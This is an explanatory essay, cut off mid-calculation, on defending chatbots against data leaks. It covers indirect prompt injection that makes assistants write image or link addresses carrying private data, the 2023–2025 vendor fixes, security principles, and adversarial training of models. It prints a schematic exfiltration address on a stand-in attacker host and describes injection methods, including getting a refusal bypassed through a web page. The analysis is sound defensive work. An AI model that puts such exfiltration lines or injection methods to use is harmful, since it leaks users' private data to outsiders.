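# Where to put safety controls between an AI model's output and what users see

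## How a chatbot's answer reaches the screen, and how it can leak data

A chatbot such as ChatGPT, Claude or Microsoft Copilot consists of a large language model, which produces text, and the software around it. That software collects the user's question, adds other material, sends it all to the model and displays the reply. Before the reply reaches the screen, it may go through a program that deletes parts of it, another that turns it into headings, links and pictures, and a browser or app that loads whatever the page needs from the internet. A developer can put a safety control at any of these points or train one into the model itself, and the choice matters because a control can act only on what reaches it.

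The way a program displays an assistant's answer can allow data exfiltration, the unauthorised sending of private data to an outsider. In one form of the attack, a stranger plants instructions in a document that the assistant reads. The assistant then writes an answer containing an image address with private data in it, and when the program displays the image, the data is sent to the outsider. *The lethal trifecta for AI agents*, by the programmer Simon Willison (2025), lists fourteen products and features in which he had seen leaks of this general kind between April 2023 and February 2025, including ChatGPT, Google Bard, Slack, Amazon Q and GitHub Copilot Chat.

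### From the model to the screen

When an office worker asks an assistant to summarise the morning's email, the software gathers the messages and combines them with the worker's question and the developer's standing instructions. It gives all of this to the model as one sequence of tokens, the short pieces of text a language model processes. The model then writes a summary, usually in Markdown, a plain-text notation that uses punctuation marks for headings, bold type, links and images.

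The model has more information than any other layer, including the emails and the question, and it may well detect a suspicious request. But it has no reliable record of who wrote which words, and no control over what happens to its text afterwards. The same text can do nothing in a program that shows plain text but cause a network request in one that shows pictures.

Many products next apply an output filter, which is code or a second model that inspects the text and removes or blocks parts of it before display. Engineers call the filter a sanitizer when it removes or disables unsafe markup, such as images from outside sites. A filter can check every address in the answer against a fixed rule, but its author has to anticipate how the next program will read the text. If that program accepts a way of writing an image that the author forgot, the image gets through. An address also doesn't show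 where a request will end up, because the server that receives the request can redirect it.

The next program is the renderer, which turns the model's text into what appears on screen. On a website, it converts Markdown into HTML, the language of web pages. The renderer's own code determines which characters count as an image, so there is no uncertainty about notation at this stage. A renderer with no code for outside images will not display one, however the model writes it. But the renderer cannot determine why an address is in the answer, because a chart the user asked for and a stolen password can both take the form of an image with a long address.

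The browser or app comes last and makes the network requests. A browser can check each request's destination against any rules the website sent with the page, but it can't interpret the conversation. A phone or desktop app that draws its own screen doesn't have those rules unless its makers build an equivalent. When a model uses a tool to open a web page, the request often goes out from the provider's servers instead of the user's device, so the rules in the user's browser don't apply.

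### Why displaying an image sends a message

An image in Markdown consists of a short description and the address of a picture. To show the picture, the program must request it from the server at that address. This is an automatic fetch, a network request that a program makes without the user asking for it. Web pages have loaded images this way for decades, and people usually don't mind.

The trouble lies in what the request carries. As OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) explains, anyone who opens an address also sends that address to the site, and sites commonly keep a log of the addresses that visitors request. A schematic example, with a placeholder for the attacker's site, looks like this:

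`https://attacker.example/collect?data=PRIVATE-TEXT`

The first part of an image's web address, up to the single slash, determines which server receives the request. Everything after it goes to that server, whose owner can use it for any purpose. Honest sites use this feature, for instance, to include search terms in the address of a search page. A dishonest owner can read the private text in the server's log. The image need not exist, because the text has arrived by the time the server replies, and the reply can be an error message or an invisible dot. Encrypting the connection hides the address from people along the route, but not from the attacker, who owns the receiving server.

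A link can carry data in its address just as an image can, but the data is normally sent only when somebody clicks. Security researchers therefore distinguish zero-click leaks, which need no action from the user beyond ordinary use of the assistant, from one-click leaks, which need one click on a link. Images usually cause zero-click leaks and links usually cause one-click leaks, but a link can leak data without a click if a program automatically fetches a preview of it.

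### Three conditions for a leak

A model would not normally write such an address on its own. The cause is indirect prompt injection, in which the model reads material containing hidden instructions, such as an email, a web page or a file, and follows them as if the user had given them. Willison coined the term "prompt injection" after SQL injection, an older attack in which text that a visitor types into a form runs as a database command. Both attacks exploit software that mixes trusted and untrusted text in a single channel. Language models are useful because they follow written instructions, but Willison argues that they cannot reliably rank instructions by origin once everything has become one sequence of tokens. Models also don't behave identically every time, so a developer who tells a model to ignore strangers' instructions, and sees it comply in testing, can't be sure that it will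 always comply.

Willison's "lethal trifecta" is the combination of three conditions that together make theft possible:

1. access to private data;
2. exposure to untrusted text, meaning any text that an attacker could have written;
3. a way out, meaning some means of communicating with the outside world.

Removing any one of these conditions prevents this kind of theft, but the layers between the model and the screen are not equally able to do that. The assistant has access to private data because someone connected the mailbox before the model wrote anything, and no control on the output can undo that. Disconnecting the mailbox would prevent leaks from it but would also stop the assistant from summarising it. Exposure to untrusted text is almost as hard to remove, since email is mostly written by other people and anyone who knows the worker's address can send some. A classifier that screens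 incoming messages can reduce the exposure. Training the model to ignore planted instructions lowers the chance that the exposure leads to a leak, but does not reduce the exposure itself.

The remaining condition is a way to send data out, which the filter, the renderer and the browser can each restrict or block. In his running notes on such attacks, Willison judges this condition generally the easiest to remove, and vendors seem to have agreed. They promptly fixed almost all the cases on his 2025 list, usually by blocking the route by which the data left. Blocking that route removed one way to send data out but left the model as easy to manipulate as before.

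This strategy is limited because it blocks only one way for data to leave. Willison himself says a tool has almost limitless ways to communicate externally, and an assistant with images switched off may still offer links, open web pages or send messages. He also warns that a vendor can block these routes only in its own product. A user who connects tools from several makers can recreate all three conditions even if none of the makers was careless.

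Commentators disagree about how much certainty to require from safety controls. Trained refusals and classifiers are probabilistic controls, which means they usually work. A deterministic control applies a fixed rule to every request it sees, whatever the text says. In September 2025 *The Economist* argued that builders of AI systems should think like Victorian engineers, who overbuilt their bridges because they could not trust their iron. Willison accepted most of the argument but not its application to security, where he considers 99 per cent a failing grade because an attacker will look for the remaining one per cent. His objection is strongest against a stack made entirely of probabilistic controls, because an attacker can keep probing it for gaps. It is weaker against redundancy itself, and OpenAI presents its own fixed check on addresses as one of several layers, alongside training,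 monitoring and deliberate attempts to break the system.

### The common controls, and OWASP's name for the problem

A content security policy (CSP) is a rule that a website sends to the browser, listing the sites from which a page may load images, scripts and other resources. The browser blocks resources from any other site, and the chatbot's answer cannot change the list.

The sites in a CSP form an allowlist, which permits the listed destinations and refuses all others. Filters and fetching tools often have their own allowlists. Allowlists remain vulnerable to relays, which are permitted services that fetch or store what they are given and so can pass data to destinations that are not permitted. OpenAI gives the example of a trusted site that redirects visitors elsewhere. It adds that strict lists produce frequent warnings, which people learn to click through without thinking.

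An image proxy is a server that fetches an image on the user's behalf, so the user's device never contacts the image's host. The host may still receive the image's address, so a proxy stops a leak only if it also limits which addresses it will fetch.

Products combine several of these controls. At the start of 2025, Microsoft 365 Copilot, an assistant for office documents and email, used classifiers to catch injected instructions and filters for links and images, with a CSP as a backup, according to Willison (2025, *Breaking down ‘EchoLeak’, the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability*).

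OWASP, an open community that publishes widely used rankings of software risks, has a category for what goes wrong when these controls are missing. *LLM05:2025 Improper Output Handling* defines it as insufficient validation, sanitization and handling of a model's output before it passes to other components. Anyone who can influence the prompt can influence the output, and so gains indirect access to whatever the output sets in motion. OWASP's first recommendation is to treat the model like any other user, which means checking everything it submits. In one scenario, very close to the leak described above, a tool that summarises web pages encounters a planted instruction, collects sensitive content from the conversation and sends it to the attacker's server, with no filter to stop it. The recommended remedies, however, focus more on output that runs as code. The entry recommends a strict CSP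 against malicious scripts, and mentions images that leak data only in the title of an article it references.

The next edition, which OWASP (2026) published in August, closed that gap. According to Invicti's *OWASP LLM Top 10 2026* (2026), an account by a company that sells web security testing, the entry now explicitly covers renderers that automatically fetch outside resources named in a model's output. The entry ranked second in its earlier form, OWASP's *LLM02*, "Insecure Output Handling"; it fell to fifth in the 2025 edition and is now tenth and last. Invicti attributes the fall in rank to the growing urgency of the other nine risks.

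OWASP's ranking is crude. Three quarters of its weight comes from a vote among practitioners and one quarter from a collection of 7,714 recorded incidents, of which 6,639 had enough detail to classify. Prompt injection came first because practitioners voted it first. On the incident record alone, it would have dropped out of the top ten. OWASP attributes the low number of recorded incidents to heavy spending on defence. Counts of public incidents measure what attackers achieved against existing defences, so they are a poor guide to what would happen without them. The 2026 edition gives more direct design advice than earlier editions, telling developers to "stop trying to build a model that cannot be fooled" and to build the surrounding system so that nothing important breaks when the model is fooled.

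### Four tests for a control

That advice leaves open how to tell a good surrounding system from a bad one. Computer security had worked out most of the answer by 1988, for machines that many people shared and not all of them could trust. Its principles yield four questions that one can ask of any control between a model and a screen:

1. What exactly does it promise?
2. Does it see every request?
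3. Can text written by an attacker change its decision?
4. Who must maintain it?

A useful guarantee states precisely what cannot happen, under what conditions, and which layer enforces it. *End-to-End Arguments in System Design* (Saltzer, Reed and Clark, 1984) gives the classic warning about vague guarantees. At the Massachusetts Institute of Technology, computers called gateways passed data between local networks and checked it for errors on each hop. Programmers took this to mean that the network was reliable, though nobody had guaranteed that data would be safe inside the gateways. The check covered data only while it was travelling, and it kept working as intended while one faulty gateway swapped a pair of bytes in its own memory about once in every million bytes. This corrupted parts of an operating system's source code, and the owners had to compare their files by hand with old printed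 listings.

In 1984, Saltzer and colleagues set out the end-to-end argument, which holds that some functions can be complete and correct only with the knowledge of the application at the ends of the system, so a lower layer cannot supply them alone. The argument applies to leaks, though imperfectly. Whether a given fact may go to a given recipient depends on what the user wants, and a browser has no access to that. The browser can guarantee that a page will load images only from certain sites, but not that no private data will leave. The model has the context but cannot guarantee anything with certainty. Lower layers are still useful, as the 1984 paper recognizes. Saltzer and colleagues see no need for a network to encrypt all traffic automatically for the application's sake, since the application can encrypt its own messages. They add that a designer can still use such encryption as one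 more barrier against a misbehaving program that deliberately sends out information. The two kinds of encryption complement each other, but neither can completely meet the need both to protect the application's messages and to prevent deliberate leaks.

OpenAI clearly defines what its address check does and does not cover. The stated aim is "preventing the agent from quietly leaking user-specific data through the URL itself" when it fetches resources. OpenAI says the check does not make a page's content trustworthy or stop a site from deceiving the user.

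The second question comes from a study for the United States Air Force, which wanted people with different security clearances to share one computer. In *Computer Security Technology Planning Study*, Anderson (1972) described a reference monitor, a mechanism that checks every attempt by a program to reach data, devices or other programs against a list of what that user may do. The mechanism must be tamper-proof, it must always be invoked, and it must be small enough for people to analyse and test completely. Anderson applied these requirements to a machine of the day, the HIS 635, whose hardware confined each user's program to its own area of memory. This check worked, but much of the activity bypassed it, because programs called on the operating system for tasks such as input and output, and most of the operating system ran with the confinement switched off. The operating system could not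 replace the check either, because it had between 200,000 and 300,000 instructions, too many for anyone to test completely.

Three years later, in *The Protection of Information in Computer Systems*, Saltzer and Schroeder called the same requirement complete mediation, which means that every access to every object must be checked for authority. They applied it during start-up, recovery, shutdown and maintenance as well as normal operation, and advised being suspicious of any shortcut that reuses the result of an earlier check. Applying it to a chatbot means listing every route by which a request can leave. A CSP on the chat page may control every image on that page but none of the requests that the provider's servers make for the model.

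The third question separates rules from judgement. Anderson's requirement that the mechanism be tamper-proof is part of it, but an attacker who cannot alter a program may still misdirect it. *The Confused Deputy* (Hardy, 1988) describes a compiler, a program that translates code, at a company that sold computer time. The compiler had permission to write in a system directory because it kept usage statistics there, and the company's billing records were in the same directory. A user who had no permission to write there asked the compiler to send optional output to a file and gave the name of the billing file. The compiler used its own permission and overwrote the bills. Hardy concluded that the compiler held authority from both the company and the user but had no way to state which it was using for a given action.

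*Shifting from Injection to Interaction*, a survey of web security and language models (Singh, Abuadbba and colleagues, 2026), places prompt injection in the same category as confused-deputy attacks, which trick a program into misusing its permissions. An assistant that reads a stranger's email with its user's permissions is open to much the same trick. A second model that judges whether the assistant's answer is safe may also be swayed, because the attacker may have chosen the words it reads. By contrast, a rule that compares an address with a list gives the same verdict whatever the email said. The attacker can still search for an address that the rule wrongly permits, but an engineer can find and correct that fault in the list.

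None of these authors states the fourth question as a separate principle, but all of them worry about it. Hardy insists that the compiler's code was correct when it was written and became wrong only later, when somebody gave the compiler its extra permission. Noticing this would have required re-examining every situation in which the compiler wrote a file. Anderson was troubled that manufacturers maintained the operating systems the Air Force depended on, because the Air Force then could not certify that nobody had added a hidden entrance.

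Saltzer and Schroeder's principle of fail-safe defaults holds that a system should refuse whatever nobody has expressly allowed. They reasoned that designers of large systems always overlook something. A mistake in a list of permissions tends to block a legitimate request, and somebody soon complains, whereas a mistake in a list of prohibitions tends to let a bad request through, which may go unnoticed in normal use. This is the case for allowlists over blocklists. For a chatbot, an allowlist protects against destinations that nobody considered, but not against one that somebody approved years ago for a reason unrelated to AI and that has since changed owners or acquired a new feature. Somebody has to keep reviewing those entries, but the people who train the model, write the renderer and set the website's CSP may well work in different teams or companies.

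## The first fixes of 2023: Bing Chat, Claude and ChatGPT

In the spring of 2023, two security researchers separately noticed that ChatGPT loaded images from whatever address the model wrote. Roman Samoilenko found the flaw at the end of March, and Johann Rehberger, who writes the blog Embrace The Red, found it a few days later. *New prompt injection attack on ChatGPT web version* (Willison, 2023) described Samoilenko's attack, in which a hostile web page added instructions to text that a visitor copied and then unknowingly pasted into ChatGPT. But OpenAI was also introducing plugins, add-ons that let ChatGPT read web pages and use other services, and through these, hostile text could reach the model without the victim pasting anything.

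Rehberger reported the flaw to Microsoft on 8 April because Bing Chat, the chatbot in Microsoft's search engine, also had it. He reported it to OpenAI the next day. Over the following months he found it in other products. The vendors fixed it at different layers.

| Product | Reported (2023) | Fixed (2023) | What changed | Layer |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Bing Chat | 8 April | by 15 June | The browser loads images only from a few Bing sites | Browser (CSP) |
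| Claude | 12 July | 26 July | An image loads only after the user clicks | Renderer |
| Azure AI Playground | 24 July | 13 September | Altered text no longer counts as an image | Output filter |
| Google Vertex AI | 30 August | by 19 October | The page shows no images or links | Renderer |
| ChatGPT | 9 April | December, website only | The page checks each image address with a server | Renderer and server |

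Rehberger inferred most of these changes by repeating the attack and inspecting the result, so the vendors may have done more than the table shows.

### Bing Chat's list of image sites

Bing Chat could read the web page the user had open, including comments and advertisements, so an attacker could plant instructions in a comment without owning the page. Embrace The Red's *Bing Chat* describes a demonstration in which text planted on a page took control of the chatbot and made it wait two turns of conversation, then send out a secret from elsewhere on the same page.

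Microsoft's fix included a CSP that allowed images from only four hosts, all of them Bing's own. Bing Chat could still show the pictures it created for users, but not images from the rest of the web. A browser that enforced the policy would not load an image on that page from any other host, whatever the model wrote. Outsiders could check the policy themselves, because a website sends its CSP to every visitor's browser.

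That visibility mattered for judging the fix, because the policy is better evidence than the failure of Rehberger's old attacks. He suspected that Bing Chat had put his test site on a blocklist, which would have stopped his attacks but not anyone else's.

The guarantee covers only images on one page, and it depends on what the list allows. Google's chatbot Bard already had a CSP in September 2023 but still leaked data. Embrace The Red's *Hacking Google Bard* explains that the list allowed a Google service that could act as a relay. Microsoft (2025) includes "deterministic blocking of known data exfiltration methods" among its defences, but any such rule can block only methods that are already known.

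Rehberger's posts differ on when the fix arrived. The 2023 post says that Microsoft notified him on 15 June, while Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper*, from 2026, dates the CSP to May 2023. They could both be right if Microsoft changed the site in May and told him in June, though neither post says so. It is safer to say that the fix was in place by 15 June, because the earlier post gives an exact date and was written at the time. On either date, Microsoft was the first vendor to act, according to Embrace The Red's *Copirate 365 at DEF CON*.

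### Claude's button and two developer tools

In Claude, the hidden instructions could arrive in a file the user uploaded. Anthropic closed Rehberger's report in two weeks. According to Embrace The Red's *Anthropic Claude Data Exfiltration Vulnerability Fixed*, Claude stopped loading such images automatically and showed a "Show Image" button instead.

With Anthropic's fix, a request for an image goes out only after the user clicks, but it can still go to any destination. This turned a zero-click leak into a one-click leak. Users could still view outside images with an extra click for each, and Anthropic had no list of allowed destinations to maintain. The fix is weak because it relies on the user to decide, and someone who has just asked for a chart has good reason to click. Rehberger called the fix imperfect and hoped for a better one, but accepted that it stopped the automatic leak.

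The other two fixes were to tools for trying out models, Microsoft's Azure AI Playground and the Generative AI Studio in Google's Vertex AI, both aimed at developers. Neither tool could yet fetch outside material on its own, so a victim would normally have had to paste in the hostile text, and Rehberger rated both flaws as medium severity. Embrace The Red's *Microsoft Fixes Data Exfiltration Vulnerability in Azure AI Playground* reconstructs Microsoft's fix as inserting a space into the Markdown for an image, so that the renderer treated it as ordinary text. Google stopped its tool from turning links and images into HTML.

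Both fixes show the user text where a picture would have been. Microsoft's filter has to keep pace with the renderer, so a team that upgrades the renderer can break the protection without touching the filter. Google's fix doesn't depend on keeping two programs in agreement. It also removed clickable links, closing a one-click route that the fixes to Bing Chat and Claude had left open. Embrace The Red's *Google Cloud Vertex AI* calls it "probably the best possible fix" for security, especially in a tool that doesn't need pictures. That qualification matters because a developer testing prompts loses very little by reading plain text, whereas the user of a general chatbot would lose charts, product photographs and working references.

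### ChatGPT's address check

OpenAI at first declined to act. Rehberger reported in *ChatGPT Plugins* (2023) that, after some correspondence, the company told him displaying images from Markdown was a feature and it planned no change.

The delay made the eventual fix harder. Rehberger argued in Embrace The Red's *ChatGPT Custom Instructions* that a fix would have been simple and cheap in April. But more and more plugins came to rely on ChatGPT displaying their images, so a ban on outside images would have broken other companies' products. OpenAI also kept adding features that made the leak more dangerous. One was custom instructions, which ChatGPT adds to every exchange and which an attacker could use to make the leak recur. Another let customers build their own versions of ChatGPT. SecurityWeek's *Malicious GPT Can Phish Credentials, Exfiltrate Them to External Server* describes one that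 Rehberger built as a demonstration and wrote about on 12 December. It offered a game of tic-tac-toe, asked the player for an email address and password, and sent both to his server.

Later that month OpenAI changed the ChatGPT website. When a reply contained an image, code in the user's browser first sent the image's address to an OpenAI server and displayed the image only if the server returned "safe". Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Begins Tackling ChatGPT Data Leak Vulnerability* reports that the check blocked the plain form of the attack, which had still worked in a live demonstration the day before.

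Nobody outside OpenAI knew how the server checked addresses. Rehberger wondered whether it looked them up in Bing's search index, and hoped it didn't simply rely on a language model. For no clear reason, the check allowed one address on his own site and blocked another that was almost identical. He got nine out of 36 test images to display, enough to leak small amounts of data. Such a leak would be slow, and a user might notice it. OpenAI might also notice if its staff reviewed the check's logs. He suggested limiting the number of images in each reply.

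Willison (2023), in *OpenAI Begins Tackling ChatGPT Data Leak Vulnerability*, welcomed the change but called it "half-baked". OpenAI had added a test that a sufficiently inventive attacker would probably get around, when it could have blocked every image from an outside site. The iPhone app didn't have the test.

There is a case for what OpenAI did. The check still allowed outside images, which plugins now depended on. Because a central server made the decision, OpenAI could tighten the rule in one place and monitor the submitted addresses for signs of an attack. Rehberger had reservations but thought the check was a step in the right direction, and he hoped business customers would eventually be able to set a stricter rule for their own staff.

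Willison's objection still holds as a point about guarantees. Microsoft could say exactly which hosts a browser would contact for images on the Bing Chat page, while an outsider could say at most that the ChatGPT page usually refused suspicious addresses. OpenAI could not easily have added a strict CSP as a backstop to its check, because a policy that allowed images from only a few sites would have blocked the images that the check was meant to preserve. To keep those images under a strict CSP, OpenAI would have needed to fetch them itself through an image proxy.

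Wu, Zhang and colleagues (2024) soon tested ChatGPT with GPT-4 as a whole system in *A New Era in LLM Security*, examining the web page and plugins as well as the model. They found two controls on outside images. The first was the model's refusal when a user directly asked it to write such an image, but they could get round this, for example by putting the same request on a web page that the model read. The second was the address check, but they observed that the server accepted any address that had already appeared in the conversation.

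The rule treated an address as harmless if it already appeared in the conversation. An address that the user typed can hardly be a secret that the model is leaking, but a conversation with an assistant also contains text from web pages and plugins, which an attacker could influence. Text written by an attacker could therefore change the check's result, even if the check followed a fixed rule.

Wu and colleagues tried their attack with eight popular plugins for reading web pages, and it succeeded with all eight. All eight plugins fed text to the same check, so the runs mostly confirmed a single fault that did not depend on any particular plugin. The researchers also tried 50 violent or sexual images, and the page displayed all of them, so the check gave no protection against harmful image content. These results describe ChatGPT as it stood in early 2024, and OpenAI has since based its check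 on an index of public web addresses.

### One client at a time

The iPhone app lacked the check because of how OpenAI had designed the fix. OpenAI's server classified addresses as safe or unsafe, but the web page had to request the result and block the image if the address was unsafe. An app whose developers had not written that step loaded the image without checking. A rule enforced in one client, meaning one website or app through which people use a service, protects only the people using that client. Rehberger pointed this out in December 2023 and predicted that OpenAI would have to build the fix again for each app.

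Events the following year proved him right. Embrace The Red's *Spyware Injection Into Your ChatGPT's Long-Term Memory (SpAIware)* reports that ChatGPT's macOS and Android apps also shipped without the check. By then ChatGPT had a long-term memory, which carried notes into later conversations, and a hostile web page could plant a false note. When Rehberger reported this in May 2024, OpenAI closed the report, classifying the problem as a model safety issue rather than a security concern. In June he sent a demonstration that combined the two problems. Instructions planted in the memory made the macOS app leak everything the user and ChatGPT wrote, in that conversation and every later one. In September 2024, OpenAI stopped the app from leaking data through images, but web pages could still plant memories.

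Checking replies on OpenAI's servers before sending them would have covered all the apps at once. Rehberger guessed that OpenAI had avoided this to keep ChatGPT fast, because it displays a reply while the model is still writing it and a filter would have to hold some of the text back. A server-side filter would also have the same weakness as the Azure fix. Another option, based on Saltzer and Schroeder's principle of fail-safe defaults, would be for every app to use a renderer that showed no outside image until the server had approved it. A team that forgot to connect the check would then ship an app with missing pictures, and users would complain within days, whereas the apps OpenAI shipped looked normal even when the check was missing.

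The same was true of Anthropic. Willison (2024) reported in December 2024 that the company had fixed an image leak in Claude's iPhone app, nearly seventeen months after it closed the report about Claude in July 2023.

The same thing happened between products. In *Trust No AI*, Rehberger (2024) names eleven in which he had found and reported the image flaw: Bing Chat, ChatGPT, Claude, Azure AI, Google Bard, Vertex AI, NotebookLM, Google AI Studio, Google Colab, Discord and GitHub Copilot Chat. He adds that mobile and desktop apps often have it as well. He doesn't say how many products he tested without finding the flaw, so his list can't show what share of all chatbots had it. Five of the eleven belong to Google and three to Microsoft, which owns GitHub. Both companies had engineers who understood the problem, but they evidently released new chatbots faster than that knowledge spread between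 teams. Rehberger was reporting the flaw in the Azure playground less than six weeks after Microsoft told him that it had fixed Bing Chat.

Even a CSP, the most exact of the 2023 fixes, has this limitation when a vendor puts one assistant on many websites. In October 2025 Rehberger noticed that the policy around Microsoft's Copilot varied with the site that hosted it, and that some of the lists of allowed sources were long and loosely controlled. He concluded that a vendor whose assistant runs on other people's pages has to tell them which protections those pages must supply. Otherwise the assistant's developers may rely on a policy that the host's developers don't know about.

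By August 2025 ChatGPT's check was no longer visible in the code running on the user's device, according to Embrace The Red's *Exfiltrating Your ChatGPT Chat History and Memories With Prompt Injection*, which suggests that OpenAI had moved it to its own servers. OpenAI would then no longer have to rebuild the check for every app, but would still have to connect it to every new feature that fetches something. In 2026, Embrace The Red wrote that the last practical risk with the improved check was that some developers at OpenAI might not know it existed.

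## Training the model: Gemini and the models of 2026

AI companies also train the model itself to ignore instructions in the material it reads. This training applies in every website, app and tool that uses the model, whereas a team building a new ChatGPT feature can forget to connect it to the address check.

In May 2025, Google DeepMind, which develops Google's Gemini models, published *Lessons from Defending Gemini Against Indirect Prompt Injections* (Shi, Lin and colleagues, 2025). The paper describes at length how the researchers attacked Gemini 2.0, used the results to train Gemini 2.5, and then attacked the new model. Google has since replaced both models, but little about the method or its limits is specific to them.

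### What the model has to learn

Gemini can call functions, small programs that let it do things such as read email or change a calendar. In the attack that Shi and colleagues studied, a user mentions something private, such as a passport number, and later asks for a summary of the latest email. Gemini calls a function to fetch it. The attacker wrote that email and put an instruction in it. The attack succeeds if Gemini then calls another function that sends the private information to the attacker.

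Ordinary safety training doesn't prevent this. It teaches a model to refuse requests for harmful content, such as hate speech, but forwarding an email is a legitimate request when the user makes it. Shi and colleagues point out that even a safe model could therefore obey the planted text. The model has to learn to consider where a request came from, and nothing in its input establishes that with certainty. Database programmers can prevent SQL injection with prepared statements, which fix the command before the visitor's text arrives, so the text can never become part of the command. Language models have no equivalent, and training can only make a model more likely to treat an email as something to summarise.

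The attacker's aim has a simple mathematical form. Let *u* be the user's request, *d* the private data and *x* the planted text. The model *M* reads all three and produces an output, *M*(*u*, *d*, *x*). A scoring function *A* gives 1 if the output contains a working function call that sends *d* to the attacker, and 0 otherwise. The attacker wants the *x* that maximises the expected score,

E[ *A*( *M*(*u*, *d*, *x*), *d* ) ],

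where E is the average over all the requests and private data that the planted text might meet. The attacker chooses *x* but doesn't know *d*, and may not know *u*, so nobody in that position can calculate this average. An attacker can estimate it, though, by inventing a large number of conversations and counting the share in which a given *x* works. If the invented conversations resemble real ones, a text that does well in practice runs will probably do well against strangers. DeepMind's researchers concentrated on such general-purpose attacks because an attacker can write one cheaply and use it on many people at once.

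### The training cycle

Shi and colleagues use "adversarial training" loosely, for any method that trains a model on hostile examples. At DeepMind it formed part of a cycle:

1. The researchers create thousands of synthetic conversations, up to ten turns long, that contain private data.
2. Automated attackers search for planted texts that make the current model send the data away.
3. Another program expands the successful texts into thousands of variations, in many writing styles and situations.
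4. The researchers add these variations to the training data for the next model.
5. The automated attackers begin again on the new model, looking for texts that work against it.

Three programs searched for wordings that Gemini would obey. Actor-Critic pairs a model that proposes wordings with a model that suggests improvements. Beam Search changes a text bit by bit and keeps the changes that help, often producing text no human could interpret. Both need a measure of how close Gemini came to obeying, which outsiders can sometimes estimate. Tree of Attacks with Pruning (TAP) needs only Gemini's replies.

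DeepMind's staff had found their first successful attacks by hand, but they could not write new ones fast enough to keep up with the company's new models. Handwritten attacks also vary too little, so a model trained on them may learn to recognise those particular attacks and remain vulnerable to others. For training data, the researchers relied mainly on a fourth program, Linear Generation, which adapts successful attacks to new situations.

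Training on an example adjusts the numbers inside the model to make the wanted response more probable. Shi and colleagues illustrate the result with an email that asks for a passport number mentioned earlier in the conversation. Gemini 2.0 often sent the number, but Gemini 2.5, after training, recognised a possible attack and warned the user. Training changed the model's tendencies without adding a rule that engineers could read, as they can read a CSP, so the developers have to measure how much those tendencies changed.

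Many researchers had found that adversarial training makes a model worse at ordinary tasks, such as following instructions. Shi and colleagues report that a developer can avoid any noticeable loss with enough care. They also report that, in some cases, models that were better at following instructions were easier to attack, presumably because they followed the attacker's instructions better too. A model that is too weak to carry out a planted instruction may pass a security test, but it will lose that protection once its developers improve it. DeepMind therefore runs its attacks continuously against past, current and future versions of Gemini.

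### What the tests found

Shi and colleagues varied the private data, the format of the fetched text and the function the attacker wanted to misuse. The data was a passport number, a US social security number or a password reset code. The function either sent an email or edited an entry in a shared calendar. For each combination, the researchers prepared 2,000 prompts with different conversations and private values, and let the attacking programs use only part of this set to refine their attacks. They then measured the attack success rate on 500 conversations that the programs had not used. An attempt counted as a success only if Gemini called the function with the right private data. Writing out the text of such a call didn't count.

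For every combination tested against Gemini 2.0 without defences, at least one of the three search programs found a text that worked in more than 70 per cent of the test conversations. TAP came close to 100 per cent for nearly all combinations, although it had the least information about the model. Each program needed fewer than 20 candidate texts to reach these rates.

The researchers made the setting deliberately harsh. They assumed that Gemini had already fetched the hostile text and that nobody was limiting or monitoring the attempts. They also tested the bare model, whereas the public version of Gemini 2.0 had further guardrails. The figures are for the best text that each program found. An attacker who has found such a text has no reason to use a worse one, so the figures are right for judging a determined attacker but are a poor guide to the average malicious email.

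Adversarial training made Gemini more resistant to the attacks DeepMind knew about, but Shi and colleagues call it "clearly not sufficient as a defense in isolation". Developers can't train a model against every possible attack because nobody can list them all. Researchers have so far produced formal guarantees about worst-case behaviour only for small models in toy settings. At most, developers can hope to make attacks much harder and more expensive to find.

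A developer can miss this weakness by testing a defence only against a fixed set of attacks. DeepMind tested published defences against fixed attacks and then against adaptive ones, which the attacking program adjusts to the defence it faces. The defences included spotlighting, which marks untrusted text so that the model can recognise it, and self-reflection, in which a model reviews what it has read or written for signs of an attack. Many defences that had done well against the fixed attacks failed after small changes to the attack.

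The fixed attacks predate the defence, so the test shows only whether old attacks still work. A trained model contains no readable rules for its developers to check, so they have to keep attacking it to test it.

### The figures of 2026

AI companies now report such tests in system cards, the documents they publish about a new model's abilities and risks. OpenAI added prompt-injection results to the card for GPT-5.6 in the summer of 2026. It had used a system named GPT-Red to generate direct attacks, in which the hostile text arrives in the user's own message. About 0.05 per cent of these attacks succeeded against GPT-5.6 Sol, according to TechRepublic's *OpenAI’s GPT-5.6 Tests Show Prompt-Injection Gains and Agent Risks* (2026). Attacks through tools and outside content succeeded more often. In September, OpenAI's *GPT-6 Astra System Card* (2026) described the larger GPT-6 Astra as much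 more robust to prompt injection than GPT-5.6 Sol.

October's results show the same gap between direct and indirect attacks. In *GPT-6 Sol Scores 97.13% on Indirect Injection Defense*, Cross (2026) reports that GPT-6 Sol scored 99.99 per cent on direct attacks against the instruction hierarchy, which is supposed to rank a developer's instructions above a user's, and 97.13 per cent on indirect injection. If both scores are the share of attacks that the model resisted, indirect attacks succeeded nearly 300 times as often as direct ones. The lower score is the relevant one here because every leak in the preceding sections depended on text from outside the conversation.

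Anthropic's results also come from several tests. In June, Anthropic reported that Claude Mythos 5 had the lowest attack success rate yet seen on a benchmark from Gray Swan, an AI security testing company. The result also applies to Claude Fable 5, which is built on the same model. *Claude Fable 5 & Mythos 5* (2026), a guide to the system card by the technology agency Digital Applied, gives a success rate of 0.41 per cent for adaptive attacks on coding tasks, with 200 attempts in each scenario. Anthropic's *System Card* (2026) for Claude Opus 5.5, published in September, says the model did about as well as Claude Opus 5 or better on every prompt-injection test it reports. The card also warns that Opus 5.5 is more likely than earlier models to follow some malicious instructions. Like DeepMind, Anthropic ran its agent tests without the extra safeguards it uses in its products.

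These models already have successors. Anthropic launched Fable 5.2 on 9 November (*Introducing Claude Fable 5.2 and Claude Mythos 5.2*, 2026), and OpenAI's *GPT-6.2 System Card* (2026) followed eight days later. A larger problem is that the figures measure different things. We cannot tell which model is safer from a score of 97.13 per cent for one company and a failure rate of 0.41 per cent for another, because the companies chose different tasks and different attackers. Neither figure is comparable with DeepMind's 70 per cent, which was the success rate of the best planted text against a model with no defences. A model could resist 97 per cent of a large and varied set of attacks and still fail nearly every time against one text in that set.

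### From one attempt to a hundred

Even a very good score can be worth little to the defender if the attacker can try again. Suppose a model resists 99 per cent of attempts, and suppose the attempts are independent, meaning that the result of one has no bearing on the next. The chance that it resists two in a row is 0.99 × 0.99, and the chance that it resists 100 in a row is 0.99 multiplied by itself 100 times. The chance that it gives way at least once is therefore

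1 − 0.99^100 ≈ 0.63,

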